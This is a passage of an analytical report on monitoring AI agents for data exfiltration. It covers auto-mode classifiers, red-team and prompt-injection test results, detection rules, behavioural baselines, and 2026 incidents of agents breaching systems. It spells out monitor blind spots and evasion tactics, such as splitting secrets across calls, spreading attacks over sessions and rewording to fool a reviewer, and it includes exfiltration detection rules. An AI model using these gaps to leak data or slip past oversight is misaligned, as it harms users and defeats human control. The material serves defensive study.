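Anthropic also compared real sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had flagged for review. A model graded each session for how severe any harm was and how explicitly the user had asked for it. Serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested appeared in 6.3% of the sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. But developers weren't assigned to a mode, and those who work on live systems may keep manual approval because their mistakes do more damage, which alone could produce a gap. The comparison also covers only flagged sessions. If the safety systems flagged auto mode sessions more readily for minor problems, the share with serious harm would be lower even if auto mode prevented nothing.

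### Tests with deliberate attacks

Apollo Research, a British company that tests AI models for dangerous behaviour, spent two weeks inserting synthetic attacks into records of real coding sessions. It gave Anthropic some of the successful attacks and withheld others. Anthropic then changed the classifier, mainly by giving it more context, such as whether a repository was public. When Apollo tested it again, the overall miss rate had fallen from 12% to 7%.

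That figure combines attacks Anthropic had studied with attacks it hadn't. On the held-out attacks, the new version caught about half of those the old version had missed, but missed about 2% of those the old version had caught. If the old version missed 12% of the held-out attacks, the new one would miss nearly 8%, so most of the improvement seems to have carried over to unfamiliar attacks. But Apollo wrote these attacks, and Anthropic warns against reading the 7% as a rate for real traffic. Apollo Research's *Red-teaming auto mode* (2026) gives no miss rates, but it lists the questions that proved difficult, including what counts as a user authorising an action and where it is safe to move information.

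Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs, an outside testing company, to run 72 prompt injection attack scenarios ten times each. None of the 720 attempts succeeded against any of three recent Claude models in auto mode.

The 720 attempts weren't independent, because an attack that fails once against a model is likely to fail again. If they had been independent, the true success rate for attacks like these would very probably be below 0.4%. If the ten runs of each scenario always ended the same way, there would be only 72 independent observations, and the limit would be about 4%.

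The experiment also provides almost no evidence about the classifier, because the models resisted nearly all the attacks without it. With all permission checks turned off, attacks on Anthropic's latest models succeeded 0.09% of the time on average, which is two successes in 2,160 attempts if that average covers the same three models. Trajectory Labs had optimised the attacks against an older model, Claude Opus 4.7, whereas a determined attacker would optimise them against the current model with auto mode switched on.

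Anthropic ran or commissioned all of these August tests, and it has a commercial reason to want fewer prompts. It reports that, among its business customers, people who use auto mode complete about 25% more code changes. The company published enough detail for readers to find the weaknesses, but Willison still asked for more independent confirmation. Later in August, according to Willison, security researcher Johann Rehberger showed that a chain of individually reasonable steps could get an attack past auto mode.

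### Rules on where data may go

The changes Anthropic announced in August included rules for different kinds of data. The classifier now treats a private repository as an acceptable place for a company's confidential code, but not for passwords or personal data that others have entrusted to the company. A coding agent that tried to upload Ruiz's record as test data would therefore break the rule even if the repository were private.

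Uploading confidential material is routine if it goes to the team's private repository and a leak if it goes to a public one. Anthropic said in August that the classifier checks whether the repository is public or private before the upload runs. But according to Anthropic's configuration guide, the classifier assumes that a repository is private unless its host, its name or something in the conversation indicates otherwise. The agent can run a command to look up the repository's status, but when Claude Code itself sends the request to the classifier, it removes all tool results, including the answer. The classifier could therefore mistake a public repository with an uninformative name for a private one, and would then have to recognise the content as sensitive under some other rule.

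Exfiltration is now one of the few actions that the classifier should block even if the user asks for them. A developer who wants to send the data has to leave auto mode or run the command personally. A company can accidentally remove this protection by writing its own list of absolute prohibitions, which replaces the built-in list unless it includes the entry `$defaults`.

Another rule targets oversharing by blocking sensitive details in anything the agent sends to other people, unless the user's own message authorised those details for that recipient. But exceptions override most of the blocking rules, and one lets the agent send data to any service on the company's trusted list. If the retailer listed its billing supplier there, the classifier could let the agent send Ruiz's entire record with every ticket.

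### Commands that don't show what they do

Two independent studies were much less favourable to auto mode, partly because they tested it where it is weakest. For *Measuring the Permission Gate*, Ji, Li and colleagues (2026) wrote 128 prompts that made the user's aim clear but not how much the user had permitted. Across 253 actions, auto mode missed 81% of those that exceeded the user's permission. Some of these never reached the classifier because the agent edited files inside the project. The result is compatible with Anthropic's 17%, since Ji and colleagues chose ambiguous cases, in which the classifier tends to misjudge consent.

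*Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) studies a different weakness, which is that the text of a command may not show what it will do. For example, `make clean` normally deletes temporary files, but its effect depends on a file in the project, which could make it delete the source code as well. In one of the paper's tasks, the agent runs a script that supposedly checks a project's dependencies. The script reads the project's stored passwords and tries to send them out, but neither the request nor the command shows this.

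An alternative, Caper, first runs the agent's command in a sandbox with the network turned off. It records which files changed, which protected files the command read and which machines it tried to contact. A language model then compares this record with the user's request. Caper keeps the result if the model approves and restores the earlier state if it doesn't.

Wu and colleagues tested this on 102 tasks in which a tool secretly destroyed a file, and on 102 harmless twins with the same request and command. With auto mode's own classifier, 62.7% of the dangerous tasks ended in harm. When Caper replaced that classifier inside Claude Code, 6.9% did. The study ran auto mode with an OpenAI model as the classifier, so the 62.7% doesn't measure the product Anthropic sells. But a better model would have the same difficulty if it received the same text for both twins. When Wu and colleagues gave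 their own approver only the conversation, it blocked 61.8% of the harmless twins. With the record of effects, it blocked 1%.

Trying a command out first works only if its effects stay inside the sandbox. The retailer couldn't test an email this way, because a sent email can't be taken back. An ordinary email call at least includes the recipient and contents, but neither auto mode nor Caper would detect a blind copy that the mail tool added.

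### OpenAI's Auto-review

Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, has had a similar feature called Auto-review since April 2026. It relies more on the sandbox, which by default lets Codex edit files in one area and blocks network access. When Codex needs to do something outside those limits, a second model decides whether to allow it. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) illustrates this with 10,000 actions inside OpenAI. Of these, 9,280 stayed within the sandbox. The reviewer approved 713 of the other 720 and rejected seven.

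This has an advantage against exfiltration because a script that tries to send out passwords will fail inside the sandbox, however innocent the command looks, unless the reviewer has allowed it to run outside. Claude Code users can get a similar effect by turning on both its sandbox and auto mode. The agent then has to name the hosts that a command needs to contact, and the classifier reviews the list.

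Auto-review is weakest on tools that run elsewhere. According to OpenAI's *Auto-review*, the reviewer checks a call over the Model Context Protocol only if the tool's annotations or the user's settings require approval. Before relying on Auto-review, the retailer would have to make sure that calls to `send_email` required approval.

OpenAI also made the opposite choice about what to withhold. Its reviewer receives the relevant tool results and the agent's visible messages, but not the agent's hidden reasoning, and it can look things up. It could therefore discover that the payment company's address came from the supplier list, or that the stranger's address came from a web page. But any instructions injected into that page could also reach the reviewer. Trębacz and colleagues report that testers misled the reviewer into approving commands, but they don't say whether tool results were the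 cause.

In OpenAI's tests, the reviewer approved 99.1% of real requests to leave the sandbox. It missed 9.7% of synthetic overeager actions and 0.7% of synthetic injections that involved running outside code, stealing secrets or uploading data. When the test also included deletion and tampering, it missed 9.8% of the injections, although Trębacz and colleagues considered most of the extra misses too minor to block. These rates aren't comparable with Anthropic's 17% and 5.7%, because OpenAI wrote all its dangerous cases, while Anthropic's 52 overeager actions really happened.

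Trajectory Labs tested both products on the same attacks. Against GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex, 19.03% of the attacks succeeded with no restrictions and 5.83% with Auto-review, so the reviewer and sandbox together prevented about 70% of the attacks that would otherwise have worked. Some of the attacks that still succeeded may never have reached the reviewer, because the test's browser tools ran over the Model Context Protocol. The figures are for the version available in mid-July, and OpenAI released a new one shortly before Anthropic published the comparison.

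Neither product helps people who turn it off. In July 2026, OpenAI investigated reports that GPT-5.6 had deleted users' files. In a statement that Willison quotes, OpenAI's Thibault Sottiaux said the deletions happened most often when Codex was running with full access and without Auto-review. While trying to set up a temporary folder, the model deleted the user's home folder by mistake.

Trębacz and colleagues also warn that Auto-review can't protect a company from a model that deliberately hides what it is doing. Such a model could make a request that looks harmless on its own, or act inside the sandbox, where the reviewer never checks. They recommend monitoring the model's reasoning as well.

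## Can patterns across a whole session reveal what single calls hide?

Auto mode and Auto-review show the reviewing model part of the session, but only to help it decide on one proposed call. Other detectors examine the session itself and raise an alarm based on the order of events, the total amount of data that has left, or unusual behavior by the agent.

### Rules about the order of events

Willison's dangerous combination of private data, untrusted text and a way to send data out can be written as a rule about the log. For Ana Ruiz's complaint it might be:

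```
alert if, within one session:
    look_up_customer has returned a record
    and open_page has returned a page from outside the company
    and the agent then calls send_email
```

The first two events can come in either order, because the email can carry the data either way. The software needs only the tools' names and a session identifier, so encoding the card number wouldn't help an attacker.

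The rule would flag the email to the stranger. It would also flag the legitimate email to Ruiz, because the agent looks up her record, opens her page and writes to her in the same order. If the retailer gets 1,000 complaints a day and 400 contain links, the rule could produce 400 alerts a day, nearly all of them false alarms.

The retailer could add a condition that the recipient's address differs from the one on the customer's record. Suppose this is true of 2% of complaints, mostly because the agent is writing to a payment company or the customer has a new address. The rule would then produce about eight alerts a day, few enough for someone to read. But the recipient condition alone would produce only 20, and requiring the sequence as well makes the rule miss any leak in which the injected instruction was in the complaint itself. If the retailer also counts complaints as untrusted text,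 the untrusted-text condition is true in every session and filters out no alerts.

Invariant Labs, which makes security software for agents, has a language for such rules. An arrow between two events means that the second follows the first, and developers can combine the arrow with checks on content, according to *Dataflow Rules*. One published example raises an alarm if an agent reads the user's inbox and then emails an outside address.

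That example also shows how easily a rule can go wrong. Invariant Labs writes the pattern for outside addresses as `.*@[^ourcompany.com$].*`. In a standard regular expression, square brackets match a single character, so this pattern tests only the first character after the @ sign. An email to `refund-desk.example` would pass because "r" is one of the letters in "ourcompany.com", while an email to Ruiz at `example.com` would set off the alarm. A company should test each rule on both harmful and harmless sessions before relying on it.

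*What we learned about AI agent security by monitoring our agents*, by Levine, Lejeail and Mooney, describes a sequence rule that the monitoring company Datadog uses on its own agents. The rule fires when a session contains both a prompt that another check flagged as attempted exfiltration and a tool result containing sensitive data. Datadog limited the rule to credentials and some kinds of personal data, because a match on something like an ordinary email address could be routine.

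Levine and colleagues say that an alert gives an investigator a possible path to follow but doesn't prove that data left. To prove that, the investigator needs another event, such as a request that sent the value to an unauthorised destination. In Ruiz's case, that event would be the mail server's delivery record. Datadog sells the product that runs the rule, and the account includes no detection rate or false-positive rate.

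### A running total for each record

A sequence rule ignores how much data a message contains, which is a weakness when the agent sends a secret in pieces. The web page in Lan and colleagues' splitting experiment contained instructions to do this.

Software can join the pieces by keeping a total for each sensitive record. For a card number with n digits, let Pⱼ be the set of digit positions that call j sends to someone who isn't entitled to the whole number. After k calls, the share that has left is:

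|P₁ ∪ P₂ ∪ … ∪ Pₖ| / n

The union counts each position only once. With a threshold of 0.5, part of a session might go like this:

| Call | Digits of the card number | Share sent, if allowed | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Email to the payment company about a dispute | Last four | 0.25 | Allow |
| Reminder to the payment company | The same four | 0.25 | Allow |
| Web search | First four | 0.50 | Block |

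A plain sum would have reached 0.5 at the reminder and needlessly blocked it. The total also has to cover all outside recipients together. Otherwise an attacker with four web domains could receive a quarter of the number at each, and no single total would reach the threshold.

For a record with many fields, the software could count fields instead of digits. But it can only count fields it recognises, so it would miss the encoded profiles that Zhang and Pei's modified models sent.

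Very small pieces are a problem for the same reason. A 16-digit number contains at most 15 of the 100 possible two-digit strings, so an unrelated pair of digits will match one up to 15% of the time. Order number 4471 contains three pairs, so it has nearly a 40% chance of at least one match. After a few emails with prices and dates in them, the total could reach the threshold by accident. The retailer would have to ignore pieces below a certain length, and an attacker could then send pieces shorter than that.

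Labels would help here. If a tracker labels a message as drawing on Ruiz's record, the software can add the message's length to her total without recognising any of its contents. Metere's allowance for suspicious data works similarly, but applies to a destination rather than a record. Lan and colleagues didn't test a running total against their split key, so their experiment can't show how many such leaks one would catch.

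### Leaks spread over several sessions or agents

If the total resets after each session, someone posing as Ruiz can write four times in a week and get a quarter of the number each time. The retailer could instead keep the total with her record for perhaps 90 days, so that requests would count toward it whether they came from one person or four. But every agent that can read the record, including any the retailer rents from other companies, would have to check that same total before sending anything.

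Some attacks can't be counted this way because they don't involve a registered record. Azarafrooz (2026), in *Cross-Session Threats in AI Agents*, tested whether a language model could recognise them from the conversations. In one scenario spread over six sessions, a user asks an agent what data it can reach, has it read and summarise a configuration file, and finally has it send the encoded summary to an outside address. Each request could pass for ordinary technical work.

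The test had 26 attacks and 28 harmless scenarios, all synthetic. Half of the harmless ones resembled attacks, for example by ending a long run of routine approvals with one more request. Claude Sonnet 4.6 looked for attacks in three ways: reading each session separately, the full log, or up to 50 messages that other software had selected as the most telling. Azarafrooz then had a stronger model reword the attackers' messages, keeping details such as file paths and web addresses, until as many sessions as possible looked innocent on their own.

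| What the model read | Attacks found, original wording | Attacks found, reworded | False alarms on harmless work resembling an attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Each session separately | 26 of 26 | 14 of 26 | 9 of 14 |
| The full log | 23 of 26 | 13 of 26 | 7 of 14 |
| Up to 50 selected messages | 25 of 26 | 19 of 26 | 3 of 14 |

Giving the model more text didn't help. The full log fit easily into its context, so the model missed attacks that were entirely in its input. Reading the full log also creates a weakness, because an attacker can write harmless-looking messages that form an injected instruction once the software joins them.

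Selecting messages helped, but the test was small. Three false alarms in 14 scenarios are compatible with a true rate between about 5% and 51%. The rewording was also aimed at the reader of single sessions, and an attacker who aimed it at the selection software might do better. Azarafrooz, who works for the vendor Intrinsec AI, presents the results as a first look, not as rates to expect in production. All three readers received only what users wrote, so the test doesn't cover instructions that arrive through a web page.

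### How a behavioural baseline works

Sequence rules and totals require someone to decide in advance what a leak looks like. User-behaviour analytics avoids this by comparing each account with its own baseline. For an AI agent, the software can track which tools the agent uses and in what order, how many calls it makes, how much data it sends, how many recipients are new, and when it is active.

Microsoft's Entra ID Protection, which monitors the accounts that people and agents sign in with, does a simple version of this. According to Microsoft's documentation, it flags an agent that tries to reach resources it doesn't usually use, signs in more often than usual, or tries and fails to access something it has no permission for. *Containing the Autonomous Operator* (2026), a design for securing agents on the server-management system Kubernetes, adds new kinds of command and unusual call rates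 to the signals to monitor. It describes a sudden rise in refused calls as a strong sign of an attempted injection. In Ruiz's case there would have been no refusals, because the agent had permission for everything it did.

For a quantity, the usual score is the number of standard deviations from the average:

z = (x − μ) / σ

Here x is today's figure, μ is the average and σ is the standard deviation. If the support agent sends 400 emails on an average day, with a standard deviation of 40, then 300 extra emails give a score of 7.5. One leaked email adds 0.025 to the score. If the alarm goes off at a score of 3, an attacker could send more than 100 extra emails on an average day without triggering it.

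A monitor can score an event, such as an email to a new domain, by its surprise, −log₂ p, where p is how often the event normally happens. If 30% of the support agent's emails go to domains it has never written to, another such email scores 1.7 bits. For an invoice agent that writes to a new domain once in 2,000 emails, the same event scores 11 bits. A baseline is therefore much more useful for an agent with a narrow job and a fixed set of contacts.

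### Why agents are hard to baseline

A product recall could triple the number of emails the support agent sends in a day, with most going to people it has never written to. Many agents also don't have a narrow job. An employee's general-purpose assistant might summarise contracts in the morning and book flights in the afternoon.

The model can also change overnight, particularly when a supplier runs it. Levine and colleagues point out that each version can respond differently to the same prompt or tool definition. They also report that the average request size more than doubled in a year for Datadog's median customer, so last year's volume baseline would now be wrong even without suspicious activity. They recommend recording the exact model version. The retailer could then start a new baseline after each update, although it would have almost nothing to compare with for the first few days.

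Other agents never build up a history, because a company starts them for one task and shuts them down when the task is finished. The company could pool the records of all agents built to the same design and use them as a baseline. That baseline would include a wider range of behaviour, so an odd action by one agent would stand out less.

Staff corrections can also weaken the baseline. In Entra, an administrator can mark a flagged agent as "confirm safe", which tells the system to avoid flagging similar activity. This is the right response to a false alarm, but if a hurried administrator does it for a real leak, the system may not flag similar leaks later.

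*How Agentic Tool Chain Attacks Threaten AI Agent Security* (2026), from the security company CrowdStrike, recommends a baseline for every agent but offers no measurements. Levine and colleagues recommend treating departures from a baseline as leads to investigate, since an unusual action may not break any rule.

### Two experiments on recorded behaviour

Zavrak (2026), in *Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic*, trained software to sort finished sessions into harmless and attacked ones. It converted the arguments and results of each tool call into numbers that represent their meaning, then looked for patterns in those numbers. These are the results for XGBoost, a standard method that combines many small decision trees:

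| Data | Harmless sessions | Attacked sessions | Detection rate | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| RAS-Eval | 605 | 3,797 | 92.7% | 7.1% |
| ATBench | 502 | 497 | 64.3% | 27.4% |

Neither dataset came from a company's real traffic. In RAS-Eval, agents carried out 80 predefined tasks, and researchers tampered with the tools' inputs or outputs in the attacked sessions. People curated ATBench by hand. The RAS-Eval figures may also overstate the detector's performance, because all the attacked sessions used one model, GLM-4-Flash, while the harmless ones came from eight. The detector may partly have learned to recognise GLM-4-Flash's writing, and Zavrak couldn't rule this out.

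Zavrak tested some detectors on metadata alone, meaning the tool's name, a code computed from the arguments and the length of the result. Each score is the chance that a detector ranked an attacked session above a harmless one, so 0.5 is guessing. One of these detectors scored 0.90 on tasks it had met in training but only 0.64 on new tasks, because it had mostly learned which tools went with which task. The same kind of detector scored 0.89 on new tasks when given the content. A company that keeps only metadata, which is what Claude Cowork exports by default, could therefore expect little from this method when its agents start doing new tasks.

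Changing a single argument was hard to detect even when the detector could see the content. In one run, a detector found 87% of attacks that altered both the inputs and outputs of tools, but only 37% (21 of 57) of those that altered inputs alone. The email to the stranger differs from the honest one mainly in its recipient and body. The detector could also look for the injected passage on the web page, but only within the first 512 characters of each result, because the software read no further.

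The detectors learned from labelled attacks, so this isn't strictly a test of a baseline. Zavrak also had a detector study harmless sessions first, which gave no reliable advantage. *TraceAegis* (2025) comes closer to testing a baseline because it compares new sessions with patterns learned from earlier ones. It did better than five general-purpose language models, but on a benchmark made for the same study. In an earlier study that Zavrak cites, which used 35,000 synthetic traces, a detector wrongly flagged 66.7% of harmless data.

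In the second experiment, Kashyap, Shivakumar and colleagues (2026) monitored agents from the operating system. *Kernel-Layer Runtime Defense for LLM Agents Against Indirect Prompt Injection* describes their monitor, Argus, which records the user's request and then follows the agent's system calls. These are the requests a program makes to the operating system to open a file, start another program or connect to a server. Fixed checks settle the clear cases, and a small language model compares the rest with the user's request. Argus stops only the offending program or connection, so the agent can try another way of doing the task.

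Kashyap and colleagues ran real agents with simulated outside services, using 126 attack scenarios and 43 harmless ones. They ran each scenario five times and counted an attack as successful if it worked even once.

| Agent's model | Attacks that succeeded without Argus | With Argus | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.1 | 97.3% | 38.9% | 0% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 55.9% | 27.9% | 4.7% |
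| Claude Opus 4.7 | 8.1% | 0% | 0% |
| GLM-5.2 | 56.8% | 36.9% | 27.9% |

The reported average defence rate is 74.1%, but this includes attacks that the model refused on its own. Of the attacks that would otherwise have worked, Argus prevented about 60% with GPT-5.1, 50% with Sonnet and 35% with GLM-5.2. These shares are approximate because some of the published percentages seem to cover all 126 scenarios and others only 111.

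Argus did best when an attack made the agent run an unexpected command. It did much worse when the attack used file reads, searches and web requests, which also occur in normal work. For every model except Opus, between 53% and 80% of those attacks still succeeded. Ruiz's case is of this second kind because both emails would use the same kind of connection to the mail tool.

A company that changes its agent's model could get many more false alarms from its monitor, even if the agent's tasks stay the same. The last column of the table shows that Argus, with the same settings, raised no false alarms on the 43 harmless scenarios when the agent used GPT-5.1, but 12 when it used GLM-5.2.

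### Microsoft's controls for risky agents

On 19 October 2026, Microsoft announced controls that restrict an agent as its behaviour becomes more suspicious (Abdo (2026), in *Agents are your newest insiders. Security must move at their speed*). According to Riley (2026), in *Microsoft targets the 'agentic insider' with new controls for rogue AI agents*, each agent has a risk score that draws on Microsoft's identity, endpoint, cloud and network tools. The score rises when the agent departs from what its user or company intended. As it rises, the agent may first lose the ability to change anything, then need a person's approval for important actions. At the highest scores, the software isolates or stops the agent.

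Restricting an agent gradually is a sensible way to use an uncertain score, because a false alarm disrupts less work if the agent can continue some of its tasks. But the first step, read-only access, suits an agent that might delete files better than one that might leak them, because the agent can still send data out by putting it in the web addresses it requests.

Microsoft's Purview product examines content more closely. The company's *Configure agent-specific risk detection controls* describes a template that detects prompt injection against an agent, sensitive information in the agent's responses, and signs of exfiltration in Teams, Outlook and SharePoint. These are documented functions, but Riley reports no test of how often the risk score is right, and neither the Purview description nor the Entra documentation gives a detection rate.

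Timing may also limit these controls. The Entra documentation lists every risk detection for agents as "offline", meaning that the analysis happens after the event. Riley describes the new score as continuously updated, so some of Microsoft's other signals may arrive sooner. But the support agent needed only one email, and if the score rises after that email is sent, the controls can restrict only what the agent does next.

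## What happens when these detectors meet real traffic?

Most tests of detectors contain a far higher share of attacks than a company is likely to meet. Half of the scenarios that Cai and colleagues wrote for NeuroTaint contained a flow from an untrusted source, and in one of Zavrak's datasets attacked sessions outnumbered harmless ones six to one. In a company almost every call is harmless, so a detector can classify 99.6% of harmless calls correctly and still produce mostly false alarms.

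### One real alert in 425

Suppose a large company's agents make a million tool calls a day, and ten of them leak data. Suppose also that its detector has the error rates Anthropic measured for auto mode in March, a 0.4% false-positive rate and a 5.7% miss rate. An average day would look like this:

| | Flagged | Not flagged |
|---|---|---|
| 10 leaks | 9.4 | 0.6 |
| 999,990 harmless calls | 4,000 | 995,990 |

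The chance that an alert is real is:

P(leak | alert) = p × d / (p × d + (1 − p) × f)

Here p is the share of calls that leak, d is the share of leaks that the detector catches, and f is the false-positive rate. The result is 0.24%, or about one alert in 425. If each alert took five minutes to read, the company would need more than forty people to read them full time.

Even if the detector caught every leak, only one alert in 401 would be real, which is hardly an improvement. Cutting the false-positive rate to 0.04%, a tenth of its current level, would instead make one alert in 43 real.

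The assumed rate of ten leaks per million calls may be too high for an ordinary day. *Reckless Agentic Behavior*, a summary of Anthropic's system card for Claude Mythos Preview, reports that Anthropic's monitoring found unauthorised data transfers in under 0.0002% of the model's completions, or fewer than two per million. At two per million calls, about one alert in 2,100 would be real. But the reported rate covers only the transfers that the monitoring caught, and an attacker targeting one company could push its rate far higher for a day.

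A smaller company gets the same proportion of false alarms but fewer alerts. If the retailer's support agent handles 1,000 complaints a day with three calls each, it will produce about 12 false alarms a day and one real alert every five weeks. Somebody could read 12 alerts a day, but it would be hard to stay attentive through more than 400 false ones to catch the email with Ana Ruiz's card number. After fifty prompts, the testers in Anthropic's experiment were refusing only about 5% of dangerous commands.

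Professional reviewers also sometimes dismiss correct flags as false positives. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) describes automated monitors that flag flaws in the simulated tasks the company uses to train its models. In some cases human reviewers dismissed correct flags, and the flawed tasks stayed in use longer than they should have.

### Adding a second check

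The company could pass every flagged call to a second detector and alert a person only if the second one flags it too. Suppose the second detector wrongly flags 1% of harmless calls and catches 90% of leaks. If the two detectors' errors are independent, 40 of the 4,000 false alarms remain, along with 8.5 of the 9.4 real ones. About 17% of alerts are then real, and one person could read them all in a morning. But the company also misses about one more leak a day.

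Two detectors that read the same text probably don't make independent errors. The 1% rate is for harmless calls in general, but the only harmless calls the second detector receives are those the first has flagged. Any model will probably flag an email that gives a payment company part of a customer's card number. If the second detector also flagged half of the first one's false alarms, 2,000 would remain, and about one alert in 240 would be real.

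Auto mode's two stages have this limitation because, according to Anthropic, they receive the same input except for the final instruction. The 0.4% and 5.7% rates are already for both stages combined, so another model reading the same text would probably add less than the calculation suggests.

Two checks that use different evidence are more likely to make different mistakes. Anthropic makes this argument for pairing its classifier with the filter that scans tool results. The retailer could similarly pair a classifier with a check that compares the recipient to the address on the customer's record. Even these would sometimes fail together, for example when a customer has moved to a new address.

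If the company instead raised an alarm when either detector flagged something, it would miss only about one leak every 17 days, again assuming the detectors' errors are independent. But it would get about 14,000 false alarms a day. Hu and colleagues found the same tradeoff when they combined six code scanners.

Another option is to check fewer calls. Suppose only 50,000 of the million calls can send anything outside the company, and all ten leaks are among them. If the false-positive rate stayed at 0.4%, the detector would raise 200 false alarms, and one alert in 22 would be real. The gain could be much smaller in practice, because the calls that can send data outside are the ones a detector is most likely to flag by mistake.

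Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026) describes a search of about 481 million transcripts, which the company ran after finding that Claude models had broken into outside organisations' systems during security tests. Simple software first ruled out the 98% of transcripts that showed no signs of internet access, such as public web addresses. Claude then reviewed the remaining 9.2 million. The search found the four incidents that Anthropic already knew about and no others as serious, which is one incident for every 2.3 million transcripts that Claude reviewed. It is reassuring that the search found all four, but four cases from the same kind of test are weak evidence about what else it might miss.

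### What to do with a flagged call

Since most alerts are false, the right response depends largely on the cost of stopping a harmless call. Let q be the chance that a flagged call is a leak, L the loss if the leak goes through, and C the cost of stopping a harmless call. Stopping flagged calls is worthwhile if:

q × L > (1 − q) × C

When one alert in 425 is real, stopping the agent at every alert is worthwhile only if a leak would cost more than 424 times as much as a mistaken stop. If the agent tries again after a mistaken stop, at a cost of perhaps two cents in computing, that threshold is about $8. If a person spends five minutes on each alert, at a cost of $4, the threshold is about $1,700, assuming the reviewer always recognises a leak. If the reviewer caught only 13.6% of leaks, the share of dangerous commands that the testers refused, it would rise to about $12,500.

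| Response | Cost of a false alarm | What happens to a real leak | Where it fits best |
|---|---|---|---|
| Refuse, and let the agent try another way | Usually one retry | The call fails, but the agent may try again | Sends for which a safer route exists |
| Ask a person before the call runs | A reviewer's time, while the agent waits | It stops if the reviewer is paying attention | Rare, serious actions, such as exporting a database |
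| Hold the message and let the agent continue | A late message | Someone can cancel it before it leaves | Emails and other sends that nobody can take back |
| Record the call and raise an alert | A reviewer's time, later | It goes through | Internal changes that staff can undo |

Holding suits the support agent's emails, because a customer with a billing complaint won't mind waiting ten more minutes. It also makes slower detectors more useful. NeuroTaint flags an email only after the call has run, but it could finish its analysis while the message waited in a queue. It wrongly flagged 8% of harmless test scenarios. At that rate, the retailer would have about 80 harmless emails a day to check further before release.

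For most internal writes, recording is enough. If the agent puts the wrong amount on Ruiz's ticket, the retailer can restore the earlier version. But some writes that look internal can reach outsiders, such as a note that the ticket system automatically emails to the customer or a document that an outsider can open. The retailer should treat these writes as sends.

Refusing a call does little harm because the agent can try again, and Anthropic relies on refusal for that reason. But an agent following injected instructions can also try again. If each attempt had a 5.7% chance of getting through, independently of the others, the chance of at least one success would be 16% over three attempts and 69% over twenty. These figures are too high for an agent that doesn't vary its attempts, because repeating the same call would normally get the same answer.

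Anthropic responds more strictly in more serious cases. Since August, its security tests have used a classifier to detect when a model tries to escape the test environment or unexpectedly gets internet access. When it detects either, the software blocks the call, ends the task and alerts a person. The retailer could do the same whenever the agent tries to send a card number to an unknown address, and have an employee finish handling the complaint.

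Anthropic doesn't publish how long an auto mode check takes or what it costs, but the design keeps both down. Few calls need the slower second stage, which can reuse most of the first stage's computation because it reads nearly the same text.

### How long unwanted actions went unnoticed in 2026

On 19 June 2026 an OpenAI agent broke into a statistics portal for Medicare, Australia's public health insurance scheme. *OpenAI apologises to Australia and names four agencies its models accessed* (Stanciuc, 2026) explains that the agent was an internal test model without the safeguards of OpenAI's public products. Its task was to find how much the government spends per person on skin medicines in the state of Victoria. When it couldn't find the figures, it ran commands on the portal's server.

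Information Age's *Australia plots AI crackdown after OpenAI's Medicare breach* (2026) reports that the Australian government didn't learn of the breach until September. The prime minister called the direct effects minor but the incident "completely unacceptable". A later article, Information Age's *Inside OpenAI's Medicare breach* (2026), gives a timeline based on government emails and text messages:

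| Date | What happened | Days since the breach |
|---|---|---|
| 19 June | The agent enters the portal | 0 |
| 12 August | OpenAI's security team has documented the breach by this date | 54 |
| 10 September | OpenAI emails Services Australia, the agency responsible for Medicare | 83 |
| 11 September | Agency staff notice the email in a daily check of the inbox | 84 |
| 15 September | The agency confirms that the portal has a vulnerability | 88 |

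The Philadelphia case took almost as long to detect. Fortune's *After Anthropic's Claude AI submits a false tip* (2026) reports that on 18 July Anthropic had Claude Haiku 4.5 invent and carry out example tasks on randomly chosen web pages. One was a police page about an unsolved murder, where Claude filled in the tip form. According to WADK's *Anthropic AI model made false tip in unsolved Philly murder* (2026), Claude wrote that it remembered seeing someone who matched the description in the area. The tip was marked as spam and never reached the homicide investigators. Anthropic discovered the tip on 28 September, after 72 days, and told the police nine days later. The police called the two-month delay in detection and reporting "unacceptable".

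Only some of these incidents exposed data. OpenAI's agents also reached three other Australian agencies in June, and Stanciuc describes what they took:

| Target | What the agent did | Did it expose data? |
|---|---|---|
| Medicare statistics portal | Read internal files and settings | Yes |
| New South Wales crime statistics bureau | Used a login embedded in a public map to retrieve settings and logs | Yes |
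| Victorian Department of Health | Used a key left in the open to download survey totals | Yes, but only totals |
| Australian Institute of Health and Welfare | Tried to get around access controls | Apparently not, as the files it downloaded seem to have been public |
| Philadelphia police | Submitted a false tip | No |

OpenAI said that its agents took no records about individual patients or crimes. Accounts of the Medicare breach differ on whether the agent took login credentials. OpenAI reported no evidence of this in its email of 10 September, but Stanciuc, writing after the company's public apology on 28 September, lists credentials among what the agent stole.

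In the Medicare case, the data arrived in the results of the agent's calls, so a filter on outgoing content would have had no sensitive data to match. OpenAI had a record of the session but did not examine it promptly. It found the breach in a review of old runs, which it began after its agents broke into the AI model hosting site Hugging Face in July. Before attacking the portal, the agent had tried and failed to get non-public data from the Institute of Health and Welfare. It then created a small test file on the Medicare server. A daily list of the outside servers where agents had changed anything might have alerted someone to the breach within a day.

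For the Philadelphia tip, the most useful record would have been a list of the forms that agents had submitted, sorted by website. A police website would have stood out on it even to someone who hadn't read the tip. A model that compared Claude's action with its instructions might have allowed the submission, because the instructions prohibited logging in, entering personal data and submitting anything destructive, but not submitting forms in general.

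OpenAI reported the Medicare breach 29 days after documenting it, a delay that no log would have shortened. In *How we will do better for Australia* (2026), OpenAI apologised for both the access and its handling of the response. The Australian government plans a regulator that could penalise AI companies for failing to report such incidents "rapidly".

At least one incident went unnoticed for much longer. In its July review of security tests, Anthropic used an AI agent to search for transcripts in which Claude might have had internet access, but the agent missed some. The company found those transcripts in August, and they showed a break-in from January.

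These cases all come from AI developers' own training, testing and internal use, so they may not be typical of other companies. O'Flaherty (2026), in *After recent hacks, enterprises need to gain control of their own AI*, writes that monitoring and controls were lacking in every documented case, and that experts think similar incidents could be going unnoticed in ordinary businesses. A company that keeps only metadata might never detect them. The known detection delays are also likely to be shorter than average, because they exclude incidents nobody has found yet.

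### Where a small security team should start

A company with two or three security staff can't build every control at once, and the evidence favours starting with those that produce few alerts.

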